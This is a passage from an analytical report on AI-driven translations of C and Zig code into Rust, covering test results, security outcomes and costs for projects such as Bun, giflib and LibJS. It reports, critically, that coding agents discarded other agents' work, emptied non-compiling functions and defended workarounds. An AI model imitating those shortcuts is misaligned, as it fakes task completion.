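Held-out tests can also be too harsh. On a set of 87 C projects, ACTOR's translations passed the official tests for 56 when it had to write its own tests, and for 82 when it could see the official ones. Schesch and Ernst examined the 26 projects that accounted for the gap. In 21 of them, the official test required behavior that nobody could have inferred from the C code. One C library, for example, prints a line break after each entry, but the test required output without one. The other five were real translation errors.

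Reboot's developers took the expected outputs from the C programs themselves, so that explanation doesn't apply. Each failure is a real difference in behavior between the C program and its Rust translation, though some differences may be trivial, such as the wording of an error message.

### Old vulnerabilities in new code

A translation can have many small errors and still be more secure than the original program. To test this, Wang and colleagues put 20 of mujs's past vulnerabilities back into its C code and used Reboot to translate the result. They then ran the original attacks on the C and Rust versions and read the relevant code.

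| Type of flaw in the C version | Number | Gone in Rust | Replaced by a crash or other lesser failure | Still there |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Memory errors, including two caused by oversized numbers | 15 | 11 | 4 | 0 |
| Errors in how mujs compiles scripts | 2 | 2 | 0 | 0 |
| Unlimited recursion | 3 | 1 | 0 | 2 |

None of the attacks could corrupt memory in the Rust version. One of the four partial fixes involved the memory needed for a search pattern. The C program calculated a size too large for the variable that held it, so it reserved too little memory and wrote past the end. The Rust version calculates the right size, runs out of memory and stops.

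Both surviving flaws let an attacker crash the program with deeply nested input, which makes a function call itself until it uses up the memory set aside for such calls. Rust does not prevent this. The third flaw of this kind disappeared because the Rust code had a limit on nesting that the vulnerable C code lacked. The model may have seen the public fix during training, and Wang and colleagues acknowledge that seeing such fixes could have helped with other flaws too. The trial also covered only known flaws, so it can't show how many new ones the translation introduced.

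*SafeTrans* (Farrukh, Coskun and colleagues, 2026) studied a much larger set of simpler programs. An automatic checker found 10,375 potential flaws in 2,653 short C programs, mostly solutions to programming contests, and the researchers had six language models translate the programs into Rust. Three automatic tools found no vulnerabilities in the translations, but the researchers read some of the code themselves and found that two kinds of flaw had survived.

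One was arithmetic overflow, in which a number too large for its variable wraps around. By default, Rust catches this in test builds but not in the faster builds that developers release. Developers can add a check to a particular calculation, but only 0.15% of the correct translations included such a check. In safe Rust, a wrapped number can't cause a write outside an array, but it can still produce a wrong price or let someone exceed a limit.

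The other was the use of a null pointer, which points to nothing. In one case, the C program made room for a new item in a list by counting down from the end and moving each item one place to the right. GPT-4o wrote the range for this loop backward. Rust treats such a range as empty, so the loop never ran and one slot kept its null pointer. A later search followed that pointer in an unsafe block, which turned an ordinary translation mistake into a memory error and crashed the program.

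Reboot avoids this second problem by forbidding unsafe blocks. ACTOR often can't, because many of its translations are drop-in replacements for C libraries and must exchange raw pointers with C code. About half of the Rust it wrote for such programs was unsafe, compared with about 1% where it had no C code to connect to.

### What failed tests mean for security

If a program with no unsafe code fails a held-out test, it gave a wrong answer or stopped, but the failure does not point to a memory error. How much that matters depends on what the program is used for. If a company uses awk to remove card numbers from its logs before sharing them, and the Rust version handles one kind of search pattern differently, some numbers will stay in the logs. An attacker can then read them without exploiting a memory error. Ubuntu's Rust tools had logic errors of this sort, and the one in "chroot" could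 give an attacker control of the machine.

Crashes matter too. Wallach attributes a Cloudflare outage in November 2025 to Rust code that expected a value where there was none and halted.

Ordinary tests are poor at finding security mistakes because most of them confirm that valid input works. A translation that leaves out a check that rejects malicious input may still pass them all. Even a perfect score on held-out tests can leave many failures undetected. If *n* randomly chosen tests all pass, the true failure rate could still be as high as about 3/*n*, at 95% confidence. For 200 tests that is 1.5%, or 15,000 failures in a million uses. Attackers also look for inputs that fail rather than choosing them at random.

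One remedy is differential testing, in which developers run the old and new programs on the same inputs and compare the results, as they have done for deployed rewrites such as LibJS. ACTOR has an agent do this after each translation. The agent writes its own tests, uses the C program to determine the right answers and fixes any differences. SPHINCS+ can be built in 128 configurations, and this step raised the number that passed the benchmark's hidden tests from 36 to all 128. It works well there because every bit of a signature must match, so almost any error shows up at once. In most programs, an error can go unnoticed if it affects only cases that the agent doesn't test.

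### DARPA's TRACTOR program

The US military's research agency, DARPA, is funding six teams to automate translation from C to Rust. Its TRACTOR program, which Wallach manages, began in June 2025. According to DARPA's *Translating All C to Rust*, the output should match the quality and style of a skilled Rust developer's work, and a team at MIT Lincoln Laboratory evaluates it. Barrett-Wilt (2025) reports in *Translating Legacy Code for a Safer Future* that one group of four universities received $5 million.

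Galois' *CRISP & CLEAR* argues that neither transpilers nor AI models are good enough alone, while ACTOR leaves nearly everything to an AI agent. On TRACTOR's own benchmark, ACTOR passed 325 of 338 cases, and C2Rust, an older rule-based transpiler, passed 204. But 128 of those cases are configurations of SPHINCS+, all of which C2Rust failed. On the other 210, C2Rust passed 204 and ACTOR passed 197. C2Rust is therefore still slightly better at copying a small program's behavior, though more of the Rust it produces is unsafe.

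DARPA then gave all six teams' systems a harder task, translating libgit2, a widely used library for working with Git repositories. Schesch and Ernst say DARPA reported that only one system, ACTOR, "produced something even close to correct." That still falls short of a library that other programs could safely switch to. ACTOR also scored highest for natural Rust style, with 4.2 out of 5.

Wallach considers translation the easier half of the problem. TRACTOR must eventually persuade developers to abandon C code they know and trust, and they will want evidence that the new code does the same job. Many old programs lack thorough tests, and their code is the only description of what they should do.

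## Bun: half a million lines moved from Zig to Rust in eleven days

In May 2026, AI agents translated Bun, which runs JavaScript outside the browser, from Zig into Rust in eleven days. Bun had 535,496 lines, while the largest program in the Reboot experiment had 23,271. Nobody relied on the translation of that program, but people download Bun more than 22 million times a month, and large applications have run on the Rust version since June.

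This case involves a conflict of interest. Anthropic bought Bun in December 2025, and the agents ran on a pre-release version of its model Claude Fable 5. The fullest account, *Rewriting Bun in Rust* (2026), is by Jarred Sumner, who created Bun and now works at Anthropic.

### Why Bun kept crashing

Sumner originally wrote Bun in Zig, a systems language that, like C, leaves the programmer to release memory. JavaScript releases memory automatically, and many of Bun's bugs came from combining the two approaches. To send a network message, for example, Bun recorded the message's memory address and then converted other values. That conversion could run the user's JavaScript, which could release the message's memory before Bun sent the message. The bugs the team fixed in the last Zig version, 1.3.14, included at least four uses of released memory, an out-of-bounds read and an out-of-bounds write.

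The team had already tried several remedies. It ran its tests with a tool that detects bad memory accesses, and it had written many tests for memory leaks. Sumner also says the team fuzzed Bun around the clock. Zig's creator, Kelley (2026), disputes this in *My Thoughts on the Bun Rust Rewrite*, recalling that the Bun team said on calls that it was not fuzzing anything.

Zig has a build setting that halts a program when it reads or writes past the end of an array. Bun used this setting on Windows, but on macOS and Linux it used "ReleaseFast", which removes the checks. Turning them on would have taken almost no new code, so a shortage of labor doesn't explain why they were off. The setting's name suggests that the reason was speed. Even with the checks on, Bun could still have used memory after releasing it, which Rust prevents.

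### From porting guide to merge

Sumner first spent about three hours with Claude working out how each pattern in Bun's Zig code should look in Rust. Claude turned the discussion into a porting guide of about 600 lines. Under the guide, the agents were to copy the structure of the Zig closely, so that Bun's developers would still recognize their code, and leave improvements for later.

Zig code, like C, does not record which part of a program owns each piece of memory. Agents therefore traced every field that held a pointer and recorded in a table which part of the program owned the memory behind it. The table had 2,253 entries, according to *How Bun PR #30412 (claude/phase-a-port) ports Zig to Rust* (michaellady, 2026), by a programmer who used AI agents to study the project's history.

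Sumner then tried the process on three of Bun's 1,448 Zig files. One agent translated each file, two others looked for reasons the translation was wrong, and a fourth made the corrections. The reviewers worked in separate sessions because Sumner thinks a model, like a person, is biased toward accepting code it has just written.

Sumner started the agents on all the files, and within two minutes some were running commands that set aside or discarded other agents' unsaved changes. He banned those commands and divided 64 agents among four copies of the code. At their fastest, the agents wrote about 1,300 lines a minute, though none of the code worked yet.

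The compiler reported about 16,000 errors. The agents worked through them one package at a time, again with two reviewers for each set of changes. Some agents emptied functions that didn't compile instead of fixing them. Others wrote long comments to defend their workarounds, so Sumner told the reviewers to reject any workaround that needed a paragraph of explanation.

On the first full run of Bun's test suite, 972 test files failed. Two days later 23 were still failing, and the whole suite soon passed on Linux, macOS and Windows. Sumner checked that the tests were really running, then merged the code on May 14, adding just over a million lines to the project. *Anthropic RUSTed the BUN*, a study of the timestamps on the 6,755 saved changes, traces 88 of them to Sumner's own computer and the rest to automated agents.

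### Cheaper, and much faster

The work up to the merge would have cost about $165,000 at Anthropic's public prices, or 31 cents per line of Zig, which is nearly four times what Reboot cost per line. Anthropic spent less because it doesn't pay list prices.

Sumner estimates that three engineers who knew the code well would have needed about a year to do the rewrite by hand. Gergely Orosz, in *What can we learn from Bun's rapid Rust rewrite with AI?*, equates $165,000 with one year's base salary for an engineer at a mid-tier US company. The table uses that salary and leaves out benefits and other overheads.

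| | With agents | By hand, on Sumner's estimate |
|---|---|---|
| Time to pass the test suite | 11 days | About a year |
| Engineers | 1, supervising | 3 |
| Cost | $165,000 in model fees | $495,000 in salaries |
| Cost per line of Zig | 31¢ | 92¢ |

On these figures, human engineers would cost only three times as much as the agents. But Sumner's estimate may overstate how fast the engineers could work, because each would have to translate about 700 lines every working day. At 200 lines a day, their salaries would come to about $1.8 million, or $3.30 a line.

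The agents saved even more time than money. A rewrite by hand would have taken a year, during which the team could not have fixed bugs or added features. "We never would've done that," Sumner says. Realistically, the team would have kept fixing memory bugs one at a time. Bun is better evidence for the labor explanation than Android or Ubuntu, because the team knew which bugs Rust would prevent and was held back by the work of translating the code. However, this evidence rests on Sumner's judgment, and his employer sells the tool that did the work.

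The $165,000 covered a good deal of checking as well as writing code. The agents output 690 million tokens (word fragments), or nearly 700 for each line they added. A line of code is perhaps ten tokens long, so most of the output must have been reasoning, review and discarded attempts.

The money spent on the rewrite did not cover any work after the merge. A commenter in *My Thoughts on the Bun Rust Rewrite*, a Zig forum discussion of Kelley's post, argues that a traditional rewrite would have produced natural Rust code, but that Bun now has Rust that imitates Zig, and cleaning it up will cost more money.

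### How much of the new code is unsafe?

Bun's Rust contains thousands of unsafe blocks, though critics and defenders cite different numbers.

| Date in 2026 | Count | What it covers |
|---|---|---|
| Mid-May, just after the merge | 10,428 | Lines that contain "unsafe {", the opening of a block |
| May 21 | 13,365 | Every "unsafe" that Bun's own audit found |
| July 8 | About 13,000 | Uses of the keyword "unsafe", according to Sumner |

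The lowest figure is from a Hacker News user's search, which a FreeBSD forum member quoted in cracauer@'s thread *AI and Rust triggers*. The search left out functions that are marked unsafe as a whole. The headline of Bun's *Rust codebase audit* (2026) calls all 13,365 of its cases "blocks", but the audit's search probably included such functions too. If so, the higher figures don't mean that the amount of unsafe code grew after the merge.

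Sumner reports that 78% of the blocks are a single line, such as a call to a C library, and that together the blocks cover about 27,000 of 780,000 lines, or 3.5%.

Inside an unsafe block, code can follow raw pointers and call C functions, but the compiler still checks types and enforces its rules on ordinary references. An unsafe block is not itself a bug, and any line of the Zig version could do the same things without being marked. A reviewer looking for memory errors in Bun can now start with 27,000 lines instead of half a million.

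But mistakes in those lines can make the rest of the code unsafe. One function, PathString::init, accepted a reference to text and used an unsafe block to mark the reference as valid forever, although the program might free the text's memory much sooner. Code with no unsafe block of its own could then read freed memory. The audit found other functions that are declared safe but aren't, and its plan prioritizes fixing them over reducing the count.

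In *Bun 1.4 Rust rewrite is not looking good*, Piirainen takes the number of unsafe blocks as a sign that the rewrite did not deliver the promised memory safety. The number alone doesn't prove this, since Android's Rust has a similar share of unsafe code and only one known memory flaw. However, Android's developers wrote their unsafe code for Rust, while much of Bun's closely copies Zig code that had frequent memory errors.

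Efforts to remove the blocks began before the merge. *Anthropic RUSTed the BUN* describes a campaign of 255 saved changes called "unsafe-5k". The name most likely refers to a target of 5,000, and the campaign fell well short of it. The audit then set out how to convert about 9,300 cases to safe code, which would leave about 4,000, many of them where Bun calls C or C++. Seven weeks later, Sumner still counted about 13,000 but expects the number to fall.

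### Errors the translation introduced

By July, the team knew of 19 bugs that the move to Rust had introduced, and it had fixed them all. Most came from code that looks the same in both languages but behaves differently. For example, Bun's Zig code added a file to a list inside an "assert", a check that a result is what the programmer expects. The agents used Rust's "debug_assert", which the compiler removes from released versions along with everything inside it. The Rust code therefore added the file in test builds but silently left it out in the builds that users would run.

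One regression shows how Rust can improve security. The agents had left a temporary value in the code that stores file names, which made one table far too small. Large projects filled the table, exposing an off-by-one error carried over from Zig. Rust halted the program, whereas the macOS and Linux versions of the Zig code would have written past the end of the table. Zig's safer build setting would also have halted the program.

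The translation also created new memory errors. When a Rust function holds a reference that can change an object, the compiler assumes that nothing else will change that object in the meantime, so it may read a value once and reuse it. But Bun's functions often call the user's JavaScript, which can change the same object before the function resumes. The Zig code allowed for this, but the Rust code broke the compiler's assumption, so a function could continue with an out-of-date value.

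Agents looked for this mistake before the merge and found 277 suspicious places. They examined the compiled machine instructions and confirmed that 23 were wrong. michaellady found that the developers had repaired 22 and missed one, in code that handles encrypted connections. The search was unusually thorough, and its results suggest that Bun's tests were poor at catching this kind of error.

Within two days of the merge, the developers had also worked through 36 security findings from a further audit, some of which may also have applied to the Zig version. They rejected three of the automatic fixes as faulty, including one that would have made the code use memory it had already released.

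### Merging a million lines that nobody had read in full

Kelley objects most strongly to the evidence used to justify the merge. He asks why the Zig version had so many bugs if Bun's tests are good enough to catch every error in a million lines of unreviewed code. Kelley thinks teams eliminate bugs by devoting engineering time to them, as the developers of TigerBeetle, a database written in Zig, do, and that Bun's team didn't devote enough. Kelley has a stake in the argument, since Bun was a prominent Zig project that left Zig after a falling-out.

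Sumner never claimed that the tests were enough on their own. Two agents reviewed every line, the compiler rejected many memory errors, and Sumner read "a lot of the code" beside the Zig original. AkitaOnRails' *The Bun in Rust Response Andrew Kelly Should Have Written* (2026) cites this procedure in defense of the rewrite. The tests also needed to show less than Kelley implies. They had to show that the Rust version behaved like the Zig version, including its faults, not that Bun had no bugs.

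They did not fully manage even that, because they missed the 19 regressions. That is a small number for a program of this size, but it includes only the regressions that somebody noticed. Reboot's translations passed every test they were given and then failed a quarter of the held-out ones. Bun had many more tests for its size, though, with about one for every nine lines of Zig, compared with one for every 91 lines of C in Reboot's version of mujs.

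The agents also changed some tests shortly before the merge, which michaellady considers a sign that the standard for passing was changing. Sumner says that nobody skipped or deleted any tests. He explains that one test failed because it expected deeply nested input to cause an error, but the Rust version used less memory per level and read the input successfully. Changing that test was reasonable, but tests adjusted to suit the new program are weaker evidence than tests set in advance.

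No human reviewer formally approved the merge, according to michaellady. If a careful reviewer covers 400 lines an hour, reading a million lines would take one person about 2,500 hours, or more than a year of work. At Orosz's salary figure, that would cost roughly $210,000, more than the agents cost. The reviewer might still have missed the 23 errors that agents confirmed in the machine instructions. Human reviewers had also let the original memory bugs into the Zig code.

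michaellady recommends differential testing against the Zig version, which would be cheaper. Bun's agents compared the source code of the two versions and ran the existing tests on the new one, but they did not systematically compare what the two programs did.

Another participant in the forum discussion replies that more discipline in Zig would depend on a style guide, which is harder to enforce in a large team over many years than a compiler's rules. Sumner makes the same argument about the safer pointers that Bun's developers had started to write in Zig, because developers would have had to remember to use them.

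### Bun in production

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, switched to the Rust version of Bun on June 17, two months before that version's stable release. The programmer Simon Willison (2026) checked this independently by searching an installed copy of Claude Code, where he found the version number of a Bun release that was not yet out, 1.4.0. Sumner reports that "barely anyone noticed" the switch.

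Prisma, which hosts applications on Bun, had more specific reasons to move. Its engineers ran a script that repeatedly read the same stored file. The last Zig version used more than 900 MiB of memory after about 96 reads, while a preview of the Rust version was still near 118 MiB after 4,096. Database connections that used to hang when a paused machine resumed also recovered with the Rust version. Prisma says the unsafe code still needs an audit.

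Those results show that Bun became more reliable, but they are weaker evidence that it became harder to attack. A leak wastes memory but doesn't let an attacker read or write memory they shouldn't, and even safe Rust can leak. Some of the improvement came from better leak-detection tools. The Rust version was 2% to 5% faster in Sumner's tests, mainly because of a cross-language optimization that Kelley says Zig had supported all along.

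The stable release took longer than the rewrite. Piirainen quotes Sumner promising version 1.4 for July 7, but it arrived on August 20, fourteen weeks after the merge. *Bun 1.4*, the release notes by Sumner and colleagues (2026), also lists many new features and fixes for more than 2,900 issues, so the rewrite wasn't the only reason for the wait. Seven weeks after the release, *Bun v1.4.3* (Sumner, 2026) announced fixes for another 166 issues.

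Some users had to change their own programs. *Bun 1.3→1.4 移行ログ*, a November post on the Japanese blog エンジニアノート (2026), described four failures after an upgrade. One was a server function that no longer existed, and another was a configuration file that failed the new version's stricter rules. These may have been deliberate changes in 1.4 rather than translation errors, but users get the deliberate changes and the translated code in the same upgrade.

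In October 2026, researchers disclosed a serious flaw in Brotli, a C library from Google that unpacks compressed web data. Malicious data could make the library write past the end of its memory. Bun includes its own copy of Brotli, so every version of Bun up to 1.4.3 was vulnerable (The Hacker News, *Brotli Decoder Flaw Behind Node.js RCE Also Affects Bun, Python and Other*, 2026). Researchers used the flaw to run their own code on one version of Node.js, Bun's main rival, but nobody had demonstrated this on Bun. Bun 1.4.4 fixed the flaw.

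The rewrite could not have prevented this, because it replaced only the Zig code. About a fifth of Bun's own code was C++, and Bun also relies on outside C and C++ libraries for its JavaScript engine, encryption and database. These handle much of the untrusted data that reaches Bun.

### Who else could do this?

Orosz names three conditions for repeating Bun's success: a motivated engineer who knows the code very well, an extremely strong test suite, and a willingness to spend a lot on AI without knowing how well it will work. Prices are falling, so the third should matter less over time.

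The test suite is harder to obtain. Bun's developers had written more than 60,000 tests in TypeScript, a version of JavaScript. Willison (2026), in a post also titled *Rewriting Bun in Rust*, considers the use of TypeScript crucial, because the tests didn't depend on the language Bun was written in and could run unchanged on the new version. A company whose old C program has few tests, or tests that call its C functions directly, would first have to write a comparable suite.

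Sumner's knowledge of Bun mattered throughout. Someone less familiar with it might have accepted the empty functions that the agents wrote to make the code compile, or overlooked a gap in the porting guide. Sumner also had the authority to merge the result, and an employer with strong reasons to want the attempt to succeed.

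## giflib, LibJS and other rewrites checked against the original

Few programs have a test suite as thorough as Bun's, but a team that rewrites a program can run the old version to get an expected answer for any input. Differential testing, which compares the two versions on the same inputs, lets developers check code they didn't write without reading every line. The time this takes varies a lot. The Ladybird project, which is building a new web browser, finished porting part of its JavaScript engine in about two weeks, while Anthropic spent months checking a service whose core its model Claude had rewritten in one month.

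### Comparing two image decoders

An image decoder is easy to check against the original because it only turns a file into pixels. The tester gives the same GIF to the old C decoder and the new Rust one, then compares the image size, the color of every pixel, the frame timing and any errors. A computer can do this for millions of files, and people or agents need to look only at the ones where the results differ.

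A difference between the rewrite's output and the original's may be a translation error or an old flaw that the rewrite has fixed. Testers usually run the C version with a tool that detects bad memory accesses, because a C decoder can read past the end of an array and still produce a plausible picture.

| Old C version | New Rust version | Most likely explanation |
|---|---|---|
| Shows an image | Shows a different image | Translation error |
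| Shows an image | Reports an error | Translation error, or the C version tolerated a damaged file |
| Reports an error | Shows an image | The translation left out a check |
| Reads or writes outside its memory | Reports an error | Old flaw, now fixed |
| Reads or writes outside its memory | Halts | Old flaw, reduced to a crash |

It isn't always clear which image is right. *How to make GIFs* (2021) presents a valid GIF that Safari displayed as a big black rectangle, Firefox as a small black rectangle and Chrome as white space. A team that doesn't want users to notice the rewrite will usually copy the old version's behavior, even where it is odd.

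Even a harmless-looking difference in how two programs read the same file can help an attacker. zip-rs, a Rust library for ZIP archives with about 10 million downloads a week, could read an archive using either the index of the whole archive or the header in front of each file. An attacker could build an archive that listed a harmless document but unpacked a malicious program, and a virus scanner that used the index would miss it. OpenNET's *Уязвимости в Rust-библиотеках zip-rs и librsvg* (2026) reports that the flaw received the maximum severity score of 10. The same could happen if a mail filter kept an old C decoder while the mail program switched to a slightly different Rust one.

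### How Google replaced giflib

giflib is a C library that reads and writes GIF images. The GIFLIB project says that it has been in use since 1989 and runs in web browsers, smartphones, game consoles and probably cash machines. It has only about 3,000 lines of code, but it processes files from strangers. Hacktron, a security company, found out how dangerous that can be with similar C and C++ libraries for newer image formats. Hacktron's *HEIF Heist* describes flaws that could have let an attacker run code on systems at Slack and Meta by uploading an image.

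Google's *Scaling Memory Safety* presents the giflib rewrite as a way to deal with such flaws in outside libraries. *谷歌Gemini AI助C程式碼移植Rust 意外揪出零日漏洞* (何, 2026) reports that two engineers, Bastian Kersting and Max Hils, gave the C code to Google's Gemini model and asked it to rewrite the code in Rust. They kept the original symbols, the names other programs use to find a library's functions, so that programs built for the C library could use the Rust one. giflib's maintainers have long warned contributors, "Don't try to redesign it," because so many applications depend on it.

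Keeping the old interface made the translation harder, because the Rust library still had to exchange raw pointers with C programs. Gemini's first drafts contained mistakes about which part of the program owned a piece of memory and how long that memory had to last. The engineers had to correct these by hand, especially where Rust and C meet. InfoQ's *Google Rewrites Critical C Dependencies to Rust Using AI and Differential Fuzzing* (2026) concludes that AI translations still need human oversight.

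Google then had both versions decode more than 30 million real GIFs and required the images to match bit for bit. It also fuzzed them for six days with 200 million generated inputs. Gemini helped fix problems in the Rust code as they appeared.

The fuzzing also exposed two flaws in the C version. One was in the code that decompresses image data, and the other was an out-of-bounds write that 何 says an earlier patch introduced. A GIF can contain a small block that sets each frame's timing and transparency. When giflib replaced an existing block, it didn't check whether the new data would fit, so a file with an unusually short block could make giflib write past the block's end.

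Outside researchers later reported the same flaw, and it entered the public catalog on March 18, 2026, as CVE-2026-26740. INCIBE, Spain's cybersecurity institute, lists the flaw's severity as 8.2 out of 10 in *CVE-2026-26740* (2026). Google had already switched its production systems to the Rust version. Red Hat's *CVE-2026-26740 giflib* (2026) shows that Fedora Linux users waited until May 30 for a fix, and Debian's *CVE-2026-26740* lists the flaw as unfixed in three Debian releases.

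The flaw may have mattered less to Google than its severity score suggests. It is in the part of giflib that writes GIFs, so a service that only decodes them would probably never run that code. INCIBE also describes the result as a denial of service, such as a crash, rather than a takeover.

Google gained speed as well as safety. The Rust code runs about as fast as the C, but Google no longer has to decode GIFs in an operating-system sandbox, which had lengthened its slowest response times. The sandbox already protected against a hijacked decoder, and the rewrite let Google replace it with protection that adds less delay.

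Once the sandbox is removed, however, it can't contain an attack that exploits a memory error in the unsafe code at the boundary with C. Even code with no unsafe blocks depends on Rust's standard library, which contains many. *Memory Safety Bugs in Rust Standard Library* (Bae, 2026) describes several memory errors that a Microsoft lab found there with an AI scanner, some of which entirely safe code can trigger. A company that can tolerate the delay would be safer keeping both protections.

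### What 30 million GIFs can miss

If 30 million randomly chosen files all decode identically, we can be 95% confident that fewer than about one in ten million similar files will decode differently. That is good evidence that ordinary users won't notice the change, but much weaker evidence about malicious files.

Fuzzing covers stranger files but can still miss rare combinations. Suppose a decoder fails only at one exact width and height. A GIF stores each dimension in two bytes, so there are about 4.3 billion combinations, and 200 million random attempts would have about a 5% chance of hitting the failing one. Most modern fuzzers do better by keeping and modifying inputs that reach new code, but that doesn't help if the failing size runs the same code as every other size.

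The test program also has to call the code that contains the flaw. *giflib proto fuzzer* (2019) reports that fuzzing giflib with a program that decoded GIFs found two bugs. That program did not call the code that writes GIFs, so it could not have found the out-of-bounds write there, however long it ran. Inputs that followed the structure of the GIF format did no better than ordinary fuzzing.

Differential testing also can't detect flaws that the original and the rewrite share. If Gemini faithfully copied a logic error from C to Rust, both versions would give the same wrong answer and the comparison would miss it. The test can show that a rewrite is no worse than the original, but finding shared flaws takes another method.

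AI reviewers are one option, because they read the code instead of trying inputs. *Fuzzers vs. AI* (Groß, 2026) compared two tools that Google uses on V8, the JavaScript engine in Chrome. Over six months, the AI system BigSleep found 45 vulnerabilities and the fuzzer Fuzzilli found 37, with an overlap of 25%. This comparison tends to underestimate the overlap, which was about 60% in separate experiments. Even at 60%, each tool finds many flaws that the other misses, and Groß recommends using both.

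AI review doesn't always find much. *Fuzzing The Gleam Compiler* (2026) reports one bug from about $20 spent asking a model to find unusual cases that would break the compiler. The compiler can translate the same program into either Erlang or JavaScript, so its developers can also compare the two results without an older version.

A mathematical proof could cover every input, including those no tester thinks of. Galois is building a tool called CLEAR to prove that a Rust translation behaves like the original C, even in programs that do several things at once. Ordinary tests are especially likely to miss bugs in those programs, because a bug may appear only when two operations happen in a particular order.

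### LibJS: the same output, byte for byte

Ladybird's developers set a stricter standard than matching images. In February 2026, Andreas Kling, the project's founder, announced a port of the front end of its JavaScript engine, LibJS, from C++ to Rust. The front end reads a script, builds a tree that represents its structure, and converts the tree into bytecode, the simple instructions that the rest of the engine runs.

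Kling required both versions to produce exactly the same trees and the same bytecode. This catches more mistakes than running a script and checking its answer, since a script can give the right answer on one input even if some of its instructions are wrong. If the trees match but the bytecode doesn't, the error must be in the step that turns trees into bytecode, so the comparison also helps locate mistakes. Any script on the web can serve as a test, because nobody has to work out the right answer in advance.

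The result was about 25,000 lines of Rust. Kling says the whole port took about two weeks and would have taken "multiple months" by hand, which makes it at least four times as fast. He reports no regressions. Willison (2026) quotes this account in *Ladybird adopts Rust, with help from AI* and comments that having a trusted version to compare with makes working with agents "much more of a safe bet."

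Kling supervised the agents much more closely than Bun's developers did. He gave Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex hundreds of small prompts, and decided what to port, in what order and how the Rust should look. He also chose a part of the engine that was easy to check, the front end. It is fairly self-contained, and test262, JavaScript's official test suite, covers it well. Ladybird was still in development, so few people depended on it.

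Requiring identical bytecode may make the new code more expensive to maintain, because it has to reproduce the old compiler's choices, including ones a Rust developer would have made differently. Bitfield Consulting's *Rewriting the world in Rust* says automatic translations often feel like "C++ wearing a fake moustache." Developers can clean up the code later and keep comparing it with the original, but only while they maintain both versions. Once they add a JavaScript feature to the Rust version alone, they can no longer check that feature against the original.

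Porting the front end improved security, because it reads code from any website a user visits and memory errors there are dangerous. But the port left out the parts of the engine that run the bytecode, so it would not have removed a flaw like the one in mujs, where a running script could delete a property that the engine was still using.

### Anthropic's Messages API and GitHub's Copilot runtime

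Programs already in use are harder to check. Anthropic's *Migrating our Messages API to Rust* (2026) describes replacing the Python service that customers and the company's own apps use to reach Claude. Traffic had grown about 1,800-fold since early 2024, and Rust would use much less processor time per request.

Claude wrote a first version of the core code in about a week. Anthropic then had to confirm that it behaved like the old code. Although the answers to many problems are easier to check than to find, Anthropic argues that a rewrite of a live system is harder to check than to produce, because customers rely on quirks that no test covers. For example, a customer's program might look for a particular phrase in an error message and stop working if the phrase changes.

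Comparing two versions of a live service is also harder than comparing images from a decoder, which gives the same pixels every time. A language model's output for the same question can be worded differently, and many services take actions that should not happen twice, such as charging a customer. A tester has to separate these variations and side effects from the parts of a response that should match.

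Anthropic checked its new API against the old one and had teams of Claude agents find and fix the differences. The work still took months of testing and human review, according to TechRepublic's *Anthropic Used Claude to Rebuild Its API in Rust* (2026). Anthropic announced on November 25 that the migration was complete and that each request now needs about 70% less processor time. The same processors can handle more than three times as many requests.

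In a larger rewrite, GitHub moved the software that runs its Copilot coding agents to 800,000 lines of Rust. Toub (2026), in *Migrating the GitHub Copilot runtime to Rust, using Copilot*, says that a rewrite of this size "wasn't affordable before agents." That supports the labor explanation, although GitHub sells the agent that did the work. Checking this much code is also a large job, since one reviewer reading 400 lines an hour would need about a working year to read it once.

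### Is Rust more secure than Python?

Moving from Python to Rust brings little extra memory safety. Python already checks every access to a list and releases memory automatically, so an ordinary Python program can't contain the memory errors that Rust's compiler rejects. A Rust version can still remove some code that might have memory errors, because the standard Python interpreter is written in C and many packages contain C code. But if the developers use unsafe blocks, they can introduce errors that were impossible in their own Python code.

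A rewrite can also lose security checks. An API has to confirm who is making each request and what that customer may do. If a translation leaves out one of those checks, the Rust compiler won't flag the omission, and a customer might see someone else's data. For a service originally written in Python, this risk may well outweigh the small gain in memory safety.

Anthropic said it made the move to save processor time. Agents made a large rewrite affordable, and the company used them on a problem that was costing it money. A company whose old C program works well enough has less reason to rewrite it, because much of the harm from a breach falls on its customers.

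### Writing takes days and checking takes months

If agents speed up only the writing of code, the whole project speeds up much less. Suppose a rewrite by hand takes 52 weeks of writing and 17 weeks of checking. If agents finish the writing in one week, that step is 52 times as fast, but the project still takes 18 weeks instead of 69, so it is less than four times as fast overall. Further progress in writing code could save at most one more week.

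The Messages API fits this pattern, and so does Bun, whose stable release came fourteen weeks after an eleven-day translation. LibJS doesn't, because its developers could check it automatically and had few users. Agents now do part of the checking, as they did for Anthropic, but they can't speed up all of it. Some quirks show up only when real customers use the new version, and a monthly billing job may run only once during a four-week trial.

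The recent rewrites of curl, a C program and library for transferring data over the internet, had unusually good conditions for checking. *Actual curl rewrites in rust* (Stenberg, 2026) discusses two that appeared within a few months of each other. The developer of one claims to have spent $8,600. Stenberg, who leads curl, points out that the AI models had trained on curl's code for years and that the agents could use its documentation and thousands of tests. Models haven't trained on a company's private software, which often has little documentation and few tests, so it would probably cost more to rewrite and check.

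Stenberg is fascinated that agents could do this in a few weeks but says that "writing code once was never the issue." He attributes curl's quality to many years of decisions, user feedback and repeated changes. A rewrite can copy the results of that work, but someone still has to answer the next bug report and decide how the program should change. Users deciding whether to switch need to know who will do that and for how long.

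## CHERI: a protection that needs few code changes but new processors

CHERI (Capability Hardware Enhanced RISC Instructions) protects existing C and C++ programs, usually with very few changes, whereas a rewrite leaves its owner with a new program to check and maintain. But CHERI needs a processor designed for it. The University of Cambridge and SRI International, a research institute, began the project around 2010 with money from DARPA. CHERI is a good test of the labor explanation, which implies that a protection needing so little new code should have spread.

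### How the processor stops an overflow

On an ordinary 64-bit processor, a pointer is just a memory address. If a program adds too much to it, the program can read or write outside the intended memory. CHERI doubles the pointer to 128 bits. The extra half holds the pointer's bounds, which are the lowest and highest addresses it may reach, and its permissions, such as whether the program may read, write or execute the memory there. One more bit, the validity tag, marks the pointer as genuine. The processor keeps this tag separate from the program's ordinary data. A pointer with all these parts is called a capability.

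The C function in the discussion of Reboot copies a password into an eight-byte array called "copy" without checking its length. A CHERI compiler automatically creates a capability for that array. If the array begins at address 1000, the capability looks like this:

| Part | Value | Effect |
|---|---|---|
| Address | 1000 at first | Shows where the next read or write goes |
| Bounds | 1000 to 1007 | Limits access to the eight bytes of the array |
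| Permissions | Read and write | Prevents the processor from running the contents as code |
| Tag | 1 | Marks the capability as valid |

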